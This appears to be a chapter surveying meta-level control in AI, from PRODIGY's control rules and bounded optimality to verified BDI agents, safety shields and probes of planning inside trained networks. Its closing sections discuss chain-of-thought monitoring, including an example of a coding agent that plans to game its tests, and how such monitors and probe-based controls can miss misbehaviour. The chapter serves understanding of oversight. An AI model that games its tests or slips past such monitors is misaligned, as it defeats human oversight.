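PRODIGY, a planning system from Carnegie Mellon University, learned control rules but kept them in a separate format from its operators. Its rules could select, reject or prefer a goal or an operator. Steven Minton built the component that learned these rules through explanation-based learning. After PRODIGY solved a problem, this component picked out a choice that had succeeded or failed, used the description of the domain to prove why, and turned the general form of the proof into a rule.

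Suppose the goal is for a robot arm to hold a block that is lying on the table. PRODIGY might consider its operator for lifting one block off another, but the arm would first have to stack the block on something, which requires already holding the block. The system can learn from this failure to reject the operator whenever the block is on the table.

Every such rule is correct, since it comes with a proof, yet adding enough of them can make the planner slower. PRODIGY has to check a rule's conditions whenever the rule might be relevant, including all the times it turns out not to apply. Minton called this the utility problem and measured each rule by a formula:

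```
utility = (average savings × frequency of use) - average matching cost
```

The average savings are the search time the rule avoids when it applies. The frequency of use is the proportion of checks on which it applies, and the matching cost is the time one check takes. If a rule saves 200 milliseconds of search, applies on one check in 20, and takes 15 milliseconds to check, its utility is 200 × 0.05 − 15, or −5 milliseconds per check, so PRODIGY would be faster without it. If checking took 4 milliseconds, the utility would be +6 and the rule would be worth keeping. PRODIGY estimated the savings from the problem that had produced the rule, measured the other two quantities as it solved more problems, and discarded rules with negative utility.

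Minton ran experiments on stacking blocks, moving a robot between rooms and scheduling a machine shop. PRODIGY solved problems faster with its learned rules than without them, and it did worse when Minton switched off the utility test. Oren Etzioni later obtained control rules for the same domains with STATIC, a program that analysed the domain descriptions without solving any practice problems. Its rules were up to three times as effective as PRODIGY's. Solving practice problems was therefore not essential to finding good control rules, though it supplied the measurements PRODIGY used to throw out bad ones.

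Soar had a similar problem. Milind Tambe, working with Newell and Rosenbloom, found that some chunks took so long to match that Soar ran more slowly after learning them. They responded by restricting how Soar could represent facts, which limited how long any one chunk could take to match.

Minton's formula is close to the value of computation, but it averages the time a rule saves and the time it takes over many uses. Neither measure takes readability into account. People could inspect PRODIGY's rules, but the system kept or discarded them based only on speed, so a broad rule that explained its strategy well could be the first discarded if it was slow to match.

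In Soar, speed also determines where control takes place. Deliberating in a subgoal is slower than firing a rule directly, so the more often an agent faces a choice, the less of its control takes place at a meta level. Russell and Wefald welcomed this kind of change. According to the summary of their book's second chapter in Furcy's *Do the right thing* (1999), they distinguish four ways for an agent to reach a decision, based on the type of knowledge it uses, and stress the importance of compilation, which lets the agent make the same decisions faster.

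### Bounded optimality

Russell and Subramanian take this reasoning to its conclusion by asking which *program* is best, instead of which computation is best at each moment. An agent is bounded-optimal if no other program that its machine could run would do better:

```
l_opt = argmax V(l, M, E),   over all programs l that M can run
```

M is the machine, E is the set of environments the agent may face, and V is the expected utility of what happens when M runs program *l* in E. V needs no separate term for thinking time, because events in the environment continue while the program thinks. The definition also avoids the regress, because it specifies the best program out of those that exist, and V already reflects any loss from the time a program spends choosing its computations.

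Russell and Subramanian prove their results for simple programs that run a fixed sequence of decision procedures and take the action recommended by the highest-quality procedure that finishes. In one example, three procedures have qualities of 0.2, 0.5 and 0.7 and running times of 2, 5 and 7 seconds. If the agent has exactly 6 seconds, the best program is the second procedure alone, because it has the highest quality of those that finish in time. If there is no deadline but each second reduces the value by 0.05, the best program is the third procedure alone, with a net value of 0.35. In both cases the designer makes the choice in advance, and the finished program contains no sign of it.

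Running several procedures in sequence is useful when the deadline is unknown. If the deadline is equally likely to fall at any time in the next 10 seconds, running the first procedure and then the second is optimal, with an expected value of 0.25, because the agent usually has at least a poor answer when time runs out. Russell and Subramanian apply this to a letter-sorting machine that must recognise each address before the next letter arrives. The order is again fixed in advance, and no meta level operates while the machine is sorting.

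These theorems show that an agent can be as competent as its machine allows without an identifiable meta level. They don't show that this is typical, because the simple programs they cover had no room for a meta level. Russell and Subramanian propose studying search programs that run a metalevel procedure at every step, and such a program might well be the best for harder problems. But the definition gives designers no reason to expect the best program to be readable. Russell and Subramanian predict that the details of optimal designs "may be rather arcane", and that learning will play a large part in finding them.

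How well people could oversee such an agent depends on what V measures. The utility function is part of the designer's problem and need not appear in the agent. If it measures only letters sorted, whether people can correct the program doesn't affect its score. If it also penalizes errors that people fail to notice or cannot repair, a slower program with a visible meta level may score higher. The letter sorter's environment, like the others in the paper, does not include people who revise the program after seeing it fail, so the theorems don't show how valuable the ability to revise it is.

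### Learned reasoning budgets

Language models that reason in text before answering must also decide when to stop. Each token, or fragment of a word, takes time and money, and a long chain of reasoning is wasted on an easy question. Several training methods from 2025 teach models to make this decision. Daman Arora and Andrea Zanette, for instance, used reinforcement learning with a larger reward for correct answers that took fewer tokens. Like Hay and colleagues, they essentially aim to maximize the quality of the final choice minus a penalty for computation. But Hay and colleagues' agent calculates when to stop from an explicit model of what each step could reveal, while a language model learns a tendency to stop or continue, stored in the same network that does the reasoning.

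AdaptThink, by Jiajie Zhang and colleagues (2025), trains a model to choose between reasoning at length and answering directly. The training favours direct answers as long as accuracy does not suffer. Pranjal Aggarwal and Sean Welleck's L1 (2025) lets the user set the length by stating a number of tokens in the prompt. Training rewards correct answers and penalises each token above or below that number. If the penalty is 0.0003 per token, a correct answer that takes 1,500 tokens when the prompt specified 1,000 receives a reward of 0.85 instead of 1.

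The requested number of tokens gives people a form of explicit control. Like *c* in Horvitz and Breese's formula, it affects how long the model reasons but doesn't specify which possibilities the model considers or in what order. The model has learned to follow the request only approximately. A program outside the model can enforce a strict maximum by cutting off the text, at the risk of losing the answer.

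Agents that run for many steps often lack even this much regulation. Upreti and colleagues describe systems that cannot "short-circuit", so a simple query goes through the same full sequence of steps as a hard one. They also discuss MIRROR, a test of sixteen models from eight laboratories, which found that models may have usable signals about their own reliability and still fail to act on them. Liu, Gani and colleagues (2026) draw the same distinction in *Metacognition in LLMs* between monitoring, such as judging how likely an answer is to be right, and control, such as putting in more effort as a result. Training a model to use fewer tokens targets control, and can succeed without improving the monitoring that should guide that control.

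Liu and colleagues also report evidence that reasoning models sometimes state falsehoods confidently and reinforce their own errors when they reflect on them. This evidence undermines an assumption behind the value of computation, that more thinking brings an agent's estimates closer to the truth on average. When reflection entrenches a mistake, the extra tokens have negative value even before counting the compute they use, and a larger budget makes the answer harder to correct.

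## Agents whose decision rules can be checked by proof

A token budget limits how long a language model reasons but doesn't make its decisions predictable. Some designers of robots, vehicles and aircraft have a much stronger guarantee, a proof that the deciding program will never make certain choices. Such a proof is feasible when the program is small, separate from the machinery it directs, and made of rules that another program can check exhaustively. A trained network has no such rules to check, but when one makes the decisions, designers can still prove properties of a filter placed between the network and the world.

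### Beliefs, goals and plans

Most of these proofs concern belief-desire-intention (BDI) agents. An agent's beliefs are its stored information about the world, which may be wrong. Its desires, which programmers usually call goals, are what it is supposed to achieve. Its intentions are the goals it is currently pursuing and the plans it has selected for them. Webster, Cameron and colleagues, in *Generating Certification Evidence for Autonomous Unmanned Aircraft Using Model Checking and Simulation*, point out that these terms are metaphors and do not imply human mental states. The terms refer to entries in the program's memory, so people can look up what an agent "believes" at any moment.

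The designer also writes a library of plans, each with a trigger, a guard and a body. The trigger is an event, such as a new goal or a new belief from a sensor. The guard lists conditions that the agent's beliefs and goals must meet. The body lists steps, which can be physical actions, changes to beliefs, or subgoals that trigger further plans.

In each cycle, the agent's interpreter takes an event, finds the plans whose trigger matches it and whose guard holds, adds one of them to the intentions, and carries out the next step of some intention. The agent's selection functions choose which event to handle, which plan to use and which intention to advance. These functions contain control knowledge. If a selection function always takes the first applicable plan in the file, part of the strategy is implicit in the order of the plans, much as it was in the order of MYCIN's rules.

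### Meta-level plans in PRS

*Reactive Reasoning and Planning* (Georgeff and Lansky, 1987) describes the Procedural Reasoning System (PRS), which let designers write some of these choices as plans. PRS controlled Flakey, a mobile robot at the research institute SRI International, in the role of an astronaut's assistant on a space station. Most steps in a PRS plan were subgoals, so the robot could start moving before it had worked out the details and could turn to another task if the situation changed.

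The library also contained meta-level plans, which dealt with the system's own beliefs, goals and intentions. They could choose among several applicable plans, decide how to pursue goals together, or work out how much more reasoning the robot had time for. Georgeff and Lansky give the example of a robot that is fetching a wrench when a warning light reports a fault in one of the station's jets. A simplified library for this case, in the notation of later BDI languages, might look like this:

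```
P1  +!fetch(wrench) : true               <- !go_to(locker); pick_up(wrench);

!go_to(astronaut)
P2  +jet_light(on)  : true               <- !go_to(panel); !diagnose(jet);

!repair(jet)
M1  +ready(I, J)    : more_urgent(J, I)  <- suspend(I); finish(J); resume(I)
```

A plus sign marks something new, and an exclamation mark marks a goal. The guard "true" means the plan always applies. Suppose the agent also has the belief more_urgent(P2, P1).

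The astronaut asks for the wrench, which triggers P1, and the robot sets off for the locker. On the way, it sees the warning light. The new belief triggers P2, so the agent has two intentions that require the robot to be in different places. The interpreter reports this as the event ready(P1, P2). M1 matches the event, and its guard holds because P2 is more urgent. The robot therefore suspends P1, repairs the jet, and continues to the locker.

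Without M1, the outcome would depend on the interpreter's default. If the default were to finish the oldest intention first, the robot would deliver the wrench while the jet was still faulty. The designer could prevent this by adding the condition "no warning light is on" to every plan that a jet fault should interrupt, but this would create the same problem as MYCIN's surgery clauses. With M1, an astronaut who urgently needs the wrench can reverse the priority by changing one of the robot's beliefs.

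By van Harmelen's test, M1 is control knowledge because it refers to intentions, not to wrenches or jets. But it shares a library, language and interpreter with the other plans, so PRS has no separate process for control. The control isn't well protected either, since a false belief about urgency would redirect the robot.

Flakey carried out much of the scenario. It planned a route, left its room, followed the corridors and avoided obstacles. When a person signalled a jet fault from a keyboard, it interrupted its task and worked through a diagnosis that followed real space shuttle procedures. Georgeff and Lansky credit this success to four features, including the meta-level plans, but report no comparison with a version that lacked those plans.

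### Checking every run

In *Practical Verification of Decision-Making in Agent-Based Autonomous Systems* (2013), Dennis, Fisher and colleagues use model checking to prove properties of BDI agents. Model checking checks whether every possible run of a system satisfies a property written in logic. Their tool, Agent Java PathFinder (AJPF), runs the agent's actual code instead of a simplified model of it. AJPF follows each branch wherever events could go more than one way, and stops if it finds a run that violates the property.

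Feedback controllers steer the vehicles and fire the thrusters in this work, so the agents do not do so directly. An intermediate program turns the controllers' continuous readings into simple beliefs, such as that a thruster is broken. To check an agent, the researchers remove the controllers and the intermediate program and have AJPF supply the agent with every combination of the beliefs they have chosen to include.

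One of their agents is a cruise control for a car in a single lane. They proved this property:

```
always ( the car accelerates  =>  the car believes it is safe )
```

The agent never selects acceleration unless it believes that the car is a safe distance from the one in front. It can receive four beliefs from outside: that the distance is safe, that the car is at the speed limit, that the driver is accelerating and that the driver is braking. AJPF checked every combination, even the one where the driver accelerates and brakes at once. Only two of the agent's plans include accelerating, and both require the belief that the distance is safe, so a careful reader of this short program could have predicted the result. Exhaustive checking is more useful for longer programs, where several intentions may be active and a belief may change between steps of a plan.

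In the satellite study, the agent moves a satellite to a position in a formation and switches to a spare fuel line if a thruster fails. With no thruster failures, AJPF examined 33 states in 10 seconds on a laptop. When any of the three thrusters could fail, it examined 16,609 states in 1 hour 18 minutes. The researchers also checked a stronger property, that the satellite would still believe it had reached its position after a repairable failure. They had to limit failures to one thruster for this check because the full version was too large to finish in reasonable time.

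The checks also found mistakes that simulation and testing had missed. For instance, the satellite had no suitable plan if a thruster broke after the agent had aborted its manoeuvre. Webster and colleagues found a similar mistake in an agent that flies an unmanned aircraft. The agent received fuel readings at three points in a flight but deleted the old reading at only two of them, so it could hold two different beliefs about its fuel and approve a route that was too long. Simulated flights had not exposed the mistake because the aircraft always carried plenty of fuel. AJPF found it in under six minutes and took about two hours to verify the corrected program.

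These programs are small, and the method has trouble with larger ones. In *Formal Verification of Autonomous Vehicle Platooning*, Kamali, Dennis and colleagues (2016) checked an agent that joins a vehicle to a convoy. They proved that a vehicle never starts to change lane if it never believes that the convoy's leader has agreed. Checking the agent took around 12 hours. AJPF could not reason about time, so they built a separate model of a leader and three vehicles by hand. They checked the model's timing with another tool, Uppaal, which took under three seconds.

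The verified agent had no procedures for coping with delayed messages. When the researchers added two, AJPF could no longer verify any property. This is a serious limitation, because a convoy on a real road needs those procedures. Kamali, Linker and Fisher (2018) extended the approach in *Modular Verification of Vehicle Platooning with Respect to Decisions, Space and Time* by adding separate reasoning about the space each vehicle occupies. The approach is still current. *An Abstract Architecture for Explainable Autonomy in Hazardous Environments* (2026) chooses a BDI agent partly because AJPF can check the actual code before it runs, without slowing the agent down.

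### Choices, not outcomes

These proofs do not show that a car will never crash. Dennis and colleagues deliberately replace the property "nothing bad ever happens" with "the agent never believes that something bad happens". An agent that cannot detect danger would satisfy the second property, so the more useful properties connect what the agent believes to what it chooses, as in the cruise control example.

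Their search-and-rescue robot looks for a trapped person on a grid of nine squares. The researchers used AJPF to prove that if the robot never believes it sees a person, it will eventually believe it has visited every square. This result covers only the robot's beliefs. To conclude that the robot will find the person, the researchers also had to assume that the sensors are correct, that the robot moves where it believes it is moving, and that the person stays still. If the person can move, the proof fails, because the two might never be in the same square at the same time.

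Dennis and colleagues consider it an advantage that these assumptions are explicit. A proof about the whole system would also depend on assumptions about the world, but they would be part of a complicated model where users might not notice them. A proof about choices also suits a program that replaces a pilot or driver, since a regulator will want to know whether the program would make the same decision as a competent person with the same information.

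AJPF can produce these proofs only if the agent's decisions are in readable rules, separate from the continuous machinery. This is not quite the separation between object level and meta level. The deciding program directs the feedback controllers, but its plans are mostly about roads, thrusters and fuel, so they are domain knowledge by van Harmelen's test. AJPF could check domain plans and control plans in the same way.

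AJPF can check a property about beliefs only because the agent stores its beliefs explicitly. *Contemporary Agent Technology* (Bădică, Bădică and colleagues, 2025) contrasts traditional agents, which have explicitly programmed beliefs, goals and plans, with language-model agents, whose behaviour comes largely from what the model learned in training. A designer who can't inspect the decision rules can still check each action before it takes effect.

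### The Simplex architecture

In *Integrate Mixed-Criticality Components with Formalized Architectural Patterns*, Sha (2008) explains how to use a complex program safely without verifying it. Suppose a system has a fast sorting program that nobody can verify and a slow one that has been proved correct. The system runs the fast program first, but only lets it rearrange the items, not add, delete or alter them. It then checks that the result is in order, which is much easier than proving the program correct. If the result is wrong or late, the slow program does the sorting, so the output is correct whatever is wrong with the fast program.

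The Simplex architecture applies this idea to machines. It pairs a complex controller, which proposes commands, with a simple, trusted controller. Often nobody can tell whether a command is right, so Simplex checks whether the machine would still be within its stability margin afterwards, where the simple controller could keep it stable. If so, Simplex allows the command, even if it is poor. Otherwise it rejects the command, and the simple controller can take over. Sha's example is the Boeing 777, which has a sophisticated main controller and a secondary one based on the control laws of the older 747. The aircraft should stay within the range of conditions that the secondary controller can handle.

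The properties that Sha says designers must verify include protection, which means that faults in the complex part must not corrupt the simple part or the software that switches between them. This is a strong form of protected control. It doesn't require the complex part to be a program. Sha applies the same reasoning to a hospital patient who operates a painkiller pump, which must be safe however often the patient presses the button.

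### How to compute a shield

A shield is a similar filter for reinforcement learning, in which a program learns from rewards by trial and error. In *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding*, Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues (2017) compute the shield before learning starts, using a safety specification and a rough model of how the environment responds to actions, both supplied by people. The specification states what must never happen, such as a water tank holding less than one litre.

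The computation treats safety as a game between the system and its environment. The system wins if it stays out of unsafe states forever, whatever the environment does. The winning region is the set of states from which the system can guarantee this, and the shield allows only actions that keep the system inside that region.

Alshiekh and colleagues use a car approaching a cliff to illustrate the need to plan ahead. A similar case fits on a small grid, where a cart moves along a row of squares towards a cliff. At each step, the controller changes the cart's speed by −1 (brake), 0 (hold) or +1 (accelerate), within a range of 0 to 3. The cart then moves forward by a number of squares equal to its new speed, and goes over the edge if fewer squares remain. The specification is that the cart must never go over the edge.

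To find the winning region, a program starts with every combination of speed and remaining squares, and repeatedly deletes those from which no action is safe:

| Speed | 0 squares left | 1 left | 2 left | 3 left | 4 left |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | safe | safe | safe | safe | safe |
| 1 | safe | safe | safe | safe | safe |
| 2 | deleted in round 1 | safe | safe | safe | safe |
| 3 | deleted in round 1 | deleted in round 1 | deleted in round 2 | safe | safe |

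Round 1 deletes the states where the cart goes over the edge on the next step even if it brakes. For example, at speed 3 with one square left, braking reduces the speed to 2, which is still too fast. Round 2 deletes the state with speed 3 and two squares left, because braking leads to speed 2 with no squares left, which round 1 deleted. Round 3 deletes nothing, so the remaining 16 states are the winning region.

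Now suppose the cart has speed 2 and four squares left, and the learner selects acceleration. The cart would move three squares and still be on the track, but it would then have speed 3 and one square left, a deleted state from which it could not stop in time. The shield therefore blocks acceleration and lets the learner choose between holding its speed and braking, since both are safe.

A designer can put the shield before the learner, where it supplies a list of safe actions, or after it, where it replaces only unsafe actions. In both positions, the shield interferes as little as safety allows. It doesn't depend on how the learner works internally, so the same shield can work with a learner that uses a small table of values or a large neural network. Its guarantee also holds during training, when the learner still makes poor choices.

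In Alshiekh and colleagues' experiments, shielded learners did at least as well as unshielded ones. Later work covers conditions that are less fixed than the single unchanging rule behind the cart's shield. For example, *Efficient Dynamic Shielding for Parametric Safety Specifications* (2025) deals with safety specifications that contain adjustable parameters.

### When the sensors, the rules or the model are wrong

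A decision that passes the check can still be disastrous if the agent's information is wrong. Webster and colleagues assume accurate sensors in their main checks, and a shield that receives a false reading of the cart's position will look up the wrong state. The usual reply is that engineers can analyse the sensors separately and combine the results. Dennis and colleagues want to prove probabilistic statements, for example that if sensor data and actions are each reliable 98% of the time, the agent avoids believing it is in a bad state 97% of the time. In 2013 this was still a plan, and such a result would still concern only what the agent believes.

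Incomplete specifications are harder to handle, because no calculation can reveal a rule that nobody thought of. The published Rules of the Air leave out much of what good pilots do, and breaking a rule is sometimes the safest option. Webster and colleagues therefore interviewed experts and added requirements such as checking the fuel before taxiing.

Translating a rule into logic can also lose part of it. One rule requires two aircraft approaching head-on to turn right. AJPF checked that if the agent believes there is an intruder, it eventually believes it has entered its "emergency avoid" phase. The aircraft turns right only if the route planner, which AJPF did not check, then works correctly. Designers can add properties as they discover gaps and recheck the agent each time, but the proof never shows that the list of properties is complete.

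The filter also relies on a model of its environment, which may be wrong. Suppose the cart's track is icy, so that braking sometimes has no effect. The table lists speed 3 with three squares left as safe, but if the brakes fail once there, the cart uses up all three squares and goes over the edge on the next step. Webster and colleagues measured a modelling error of this kind when they added distances to their aircraft check. Their model gave a minimum separation of 1,129 feet from another aircraft, but a detailed flight simulator gave 820. Much of the difference arose because the model assumed instantaneous turns, and with a realistic turning rate it gave 929. All these distances satisfy the 500-foot rule, but the model's error was in the dangerous direction because it overestimated the separation.

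Alshiekh and colleagues address this by making the model conservative, so that it covers everything the real environment might do. The model can be very coarse, because it needs only the details that matter for safety. But if the cart's model allows the brakes to fail at every step, no moving cart is certain to stop, and the only shield that guarantees safety never lets the cart start. A useful shield therefore requires some definite knowledge of the environment.

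Physical damage can make even a good model wrong. In *RSimplex*, Wang, Hovakimyan and Sha warn that a physical failure may change a machine's behavior so much that the original Simplex design no longer works, and they propose a more robust version for software and physical failures together. Other research, such as *Dynamic Shielding for Reinforcement Learning in Black-Box Environments* (2022), tries to do without a known model. But a system that has to learn its model from experience starts with less to base a guarantee on.

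### Is a shield a meta level?

A shield belongs to the meta level under Genesereth's definition, because it helps to decide which base-level action the machine performs. Van Harmelen's definition excludes it, because the shield's specification refers to cliffs and speeds, not to the learner's knowledge or reasoning. The cart's shield would be the same if a person, a rule base or a neural network were driving.

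A shield has some of the properties that designers wanted from a meta level. It is a separate process, people write its specification separately, and engineers can protect it from the learner. But it controls only which actions may go ahead, not what the learner considers, which goal it pursues or which safe action it takes. Like a combinatorially sound meta level, a shield that only removes options adds nothing of its own, but it filters actions instead of directing reasoning. "Guard" is therefore a clearer name than "meta level" for a shield and for much of the rule enforcement around language models.

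The distinction affects how well people can control the agent. With a shield, people know some of what the agent won't do, as long as the model is right. They can find out why the shield blocked an action, but not why the learner proposed it. The shield also doesn't correct the learner's faults. A learner that keeps trying to drive over the cliff may be just as likely to drive into hazards that the specification omits. Its designers could notice the problem from a record of blocked actions, but they would have to look elsewhere for the cause.

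The meta-level plan M1 can use the robot's intentions to make distinctions that a shield cannot. If the robot heads for the locker while the warning light is on, M1 can distinguish a trip for the wrench, which can wait, from a trip for an urgently needed jet part. A shield that receives only the robot's position and speed would treat the two trips the same.

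## Control inside a trained network

M1 can distinguish one trip to the locker from another because the robot's intentions are entries in its memory. A neural network has no such entries. Training sets its weights, the numbers that determine how it turns inputs into outputs, and nobody decides which weights will hold control knowledge. When the network runs, each layer computes further numbers, called activations. Any plans, goals or strategies the network has must be somewhere in its weights and activations, and researchers have begun to find some of them.

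Such discoveries give people varying degrees of control. People can *read* a signal if they can predict from it what the network will do. They can *steer* with it if changing the signal changes the network's behaviour. They can steer *reliably* if changing the signal produces the behaviour they want even in situations they have not tried. A car's speedometer shows its speed, but pushing the needle back does not slow the car. The brake does slow the car, but not reliably on ice. Control is explicit in van Harmelen's sense only if people can both read a signal and steer with it.

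### Plans in a network that plays Sokoban

In Sokoban, a player pushes boxes around a small walled grid until every box is on a target. The player cannot pull boxes, so one push into a corner can make the puzzle unsolvable. Arthur Guez and colleagues designed a network called DRC that learned the game by trial and error, without a model of the rules or a search program. It runs its three layers three times before each move. It solves more puzzles when it has extra time before its first move. This suggests that it plans, although a large set of learned reactions might produce the same improvement.

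Bush, Chung and colleagues (2025), in *Interpreting Emergent Planning in Model-Free Reinforcement Learning*, looked for the plans themselves. They trained linear probes, simple classifiers that predict a fact from weighted sums of a network's activations. For each square on the board, one probe predicted the direction from which the player would next enter it, and another predicted the direction in which the next box would leave it. Both could also output "never". Each probe had only 160 adjustable numbers and received only the 32 activations that one layer had computed for that square. Probes given the board position instead of the activations did far worse, so the information must have come from the network's own computation.

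The predictions form connected routes from boxes to targets when drawn as arrows on the board. As the network runs, the routes grow forwards from the boxes and backwards from the targets, and in some puzzles a longer route replaces an obvious but blocked one. In 1,000 games, the researchers made the player stand still for the first five moves. The longer the network ran, the better the arrows predicted what the player went on to do.

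To find out whether these plans steer the player, Bush and colleagues built puzzles with a short route and a long one. Left alone, the player follows the short route. The researchers took the direction in activation space that a probe associated with "never" and added it to the activations for squares on the short route. At the start of the long route, they added the direction for a step along it. They counted a success if the player then solved the puzzle by the long route, and repeated the test with random directions of similar size:

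| Layer changed | Player's route | Random directions | Box's route | Random directions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 94.6% | 33.7% | 56.2% | 31.5% |
| 2 | 90.1% | 29.8% | 72.7% | 30.9% |
| 3 | 98.8% | 27.8% | 80.6% | 4.1% |

The trained directions did much better than the random ones, which is strong evidence that the plans steer behaviour. The random directions also sometimes pushed the player off the short route, which shows that merely disturbing the network can be enough to do so. The evidence that the plans can be changed reliably is weaker. Redirecting a box through layer 1 failed in almost half the puzzles, even though these were handmade with two clear routes and the researchers already knew what plan they wanted.

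In *Path Channels and Plan Extension Kernels*, Taufeeque, Tucker and colleagues (2025) analyzed another DRC network and found that it stores its plan in a simple form. Its activations are arranged in 96 channels, each with one number per square. A high number in a "box right" channel means a box on that square will go right. They classed 59 channels as parts of the plan. Erasing what these channels had stored from earlier moves cut the proportion of puzzles solved by 57.6%, while doing the same to the other 37 cut it by 10.5%.

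Changing the channels directly also steered the player better than using probes. When the researchers tried to make the player take a different action, they succeeded 53.2% of the time with the channels for the player's own movement, against 20.7% with a probe. For box movement, the figures were 86.3% and 82.5%. Taufeeque and colleagues explain that the probes had also given weight to channels that merely correlated with the plan. Changing those channels does not change the plan, and an overseer who relied on a probe's accuracy would not know that the probe used them.

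The weights between channels determine which plan wins. They extend each route one square at a time, and obstacles produce negative values that spread back along a route and erase it. If two routes leave the same box, the one with the higher activation suppresses the other. Training deducted 0.1 points for every move, yet the plan channels do not record a route's length. A shorter route usually wins because it connects the box to the target first. In one example with two equally good routes, slightly larger weights gave going down an advantage over going right. MYCIN's clause order and rule numbers had similar effects, and in both systems a person can see what will happen next without learning why.

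The part of the network that chooses between routes counts as meta-level under Genesereth's definition. But it has neither a separate representation nor a separate process, because it consists of weights between the same channels that hold the routes. Understanding those weights still gave the researchers some control. When they made the route-extending ones 1.4 times as strong, a network trained only on 10 × 10 boards solved a 40 × 40 puzzle.

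Taufeeque and colleagues found the same mechanisms in four more networks that they trained separately. Bush and colleagues also report signs of planning in a version of Pac-Man and in a different type of network, but they leave open whether a general-purpose agent would learn to plan. DRC was unusually easy to study because each of its activations, unlike those of a language model, corresponds to a square on the board, and because the researchers could guess what a plan would look like.

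### Knowing how and knowing when

A base model is a language model trained to predict text. Developers can train it further to reason at length before answering, which produces a thinking model. This further training might teach new skills, such as checking a result or backing out of a failed approach. Alternatively, the base model might already have these skills, and the training might mostly add control knowledge, which is knowledge of when to use them.

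Venhoff, Arcuschin and colleagues (2025), in *Base Models Know How to Reason, Thinking Models Learn When*, tested this by trying to rebuild thinking models from their base models:

1. They averaged a thinking model's activations over each sentence of its reasoning and sorted the sentences into 5 to 15 categories, such as verifying a result or setting a subgoal.
2. For each category, they looked for a vector that would make the base model produce that kind of step when they added it to the base model's activations.
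3. They combined the two models into a hybrid. The base model writes the answer, and the thinking model processes the same text. Where both predict the same next token, the hybrid uses it. Where they disagree, the thinking model's activations select a category, and the hybrid adds the corresponding vector to the base model.

They then measured how much of the thinking model's advantage the hybrid recovered:

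```
share recovered = (hybrid - base) / (thinking - base)
```

The largest thinking model trained by reinforcement learning solved 97.2% of a set of school mathematics problems. Its base model solved 69.5% and the hybrid 95.5%, so the hybrid recovered about 94% of the gap between the base and thinking models. On a harder set, it recovered 60%. Across four such thinking models and three sets of problems, the hybrids recovered an average of 76% of the gap while steering only about 5–12% of tokens.

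The result was very different for distilled models, which learn by imitating reasoning written by another model. Venhoff and colleagues report an average recovery of 11% for these models, but that figure matches their detailed results only if it includes a model that had both kinds of training. The four purely distilled models average about 8%. The researchers conclude that reinforcement learning mainly teaches a model when to use its existing skills, while distillation also changes the skills.

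Further tests on two of the models trained by reinforcement learning support the idea that timing and choice matter. The full hybrids recovered about 77% of the gap. When the researchers replaced the selected category with a random one, recovery fell to 20–28%. The hybrids did worse than the base models when the researchers replaced the learned vectors with random directions.

The experiment may not separate "how" from "when" cleanly. The thinking model has to process the whole text to decide when to steer, so its signal may reflect progress on the problem as well as timing. The researchers also fitted the vectors to the tokens that model preferred. Venhoff and colleagues acknowledge that the thinking model influences how strongly the hybrid steers, and that poor recovery for distilled models might result from a poor method of finding vectors. Their categories lean towards mathematics, and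 all the tests were mathematical. Some recovery percentages are also measured against small improvements. The smallest model recovered 107% on one set, but its training had raised its score there by only about ten percentage points.

Even if the conclusion is right, the hybrid gives people less to inspect and edit than NEOMYCIN's meta-rules did. Researchers built a separate control process into the hybrid, but in the thinking model itself, the same weights encode both the skills and when to use them. People can read which category the hybrid selects at each point, but there is no written rule for when to check a result, so they have nothing like METARULE002 to edit.

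### What models can report about themselves

A meta level also needs information about how the object level is doing. Psychologists call the ability to monitor and regulate one's own thinking metacognition. Liu and colleagues report that researchers have increasingly applied the term to language models since 2023 without agreeing on a definition. Some use it for any process by which a model reviews and revises its answer, while others require the model to judge its competence from its own activations. Liu and colleagues also cite conflicting findings, with some studies reporting reflective behaviour that resembles metacognition and others reporting that models are far from able to make useful confidence judgements.

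A model's confidence can be accurate in different ways. Suppose a model answers 100 questions, gets 70 right, and reports 70% confidence every time. Its confidence is perfectly calibrated because it matches the model's overall success rate, but it has no sensitivity because it is the same for right and wrong answers. Sensitivity is more useful for control because it helps identify which answers to check.

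Some researchers measure self-monitoring with a ratio from psychology, meta-*d′*/*d′*. *d′* measures how well the model does the task, and meta-*d′* measures, on a comparable scale, how well its confidence separates its right answers from its wrong ones. If *d′* is 2 and meta-*d′* is 1, the ratio is 0.5, which means the confidence is only half as informative as the model's performance would allow. Dividing by *d′* keeps a model from scoring well on self-monitoring just because it is good at the task.

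Upreti and colleagues cite evidence that models' reported confidence correlates with whether they are right. The MIRROR tests examined whether models could apply such self-knowledge in new areas, predict their success on combinations of tasks, and regulate their own behaviour. Predictions about combinations failed across the models, and self-knowledge often failed to carry over to new areas or to change after feedback. The models also failed to act on the reliability signals they did have, which psychologists call monitoring without control.

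Upreti and colleagues argue that an agent needs a monitor that follows the whole run and a controller that intervenes when the monitor signals a problem. The retry loops in current agents come closest to this, but they usually revise one answer and leave the rest of the run unregulated. Upreti and colleagues suggest testing whether an agent regulates itself by changing a task's difficulty or making it unsolvable, then checking whether the agent changes its effort or strategy. This tests behaviour directly, so it doesn't depend on how well the agent describes itself, but they leave the experiments to future work.

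In *Regulating the Agency of LLM-based Agents*, Boddy and Joseph (2025) propose connecting a monitor to a controller inside the network. Probes would measure how rigid an agent's preferences are, how independently it works and how persistently it pursues goals. The controller would then add vectors to the activations until each measurement reached the level people set with a slider. For example, an operator could make an agent in a power station ask for approval more often by turning down its independence.

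Boddy and Joseph have not tested their proposal, and the Sokoban results show how it could go wrong. If a probe responds partly to signals that only correlate with independence, the controller could lower the measurement while the agent kept acting alone. They plan to choose layers by how much changing them affects behaviour, which should help, but they would still need to check the agent's actions as well as the slider.

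### Written reasoning as a record of control

A thinking model also writes out its reasoning, or chain of thought, in ordinary language before it answers or acts, so this reasoning can be read without a probe. If a coding agent writes that the tests check only one value and that it will simply return that value, a person or another program can stop it before it submits the code. In *Chain of Thought Monitorability*, Korbak, Balesni and colleagues (2025) call such monitoring a unique opportunity for safety, but warn that it will miss some misbehaviour and that the opportunity may be fragile.

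NEOMYCIN's explanations were reliable because the program built them from the meta-rules that had chosen its questions. A language model's written reasoning doesn't come with that guarantee. The text can influence the answer because the model takes it as input when generating later tokens, but part of the decision may happen in activations that the text doesn't describe.

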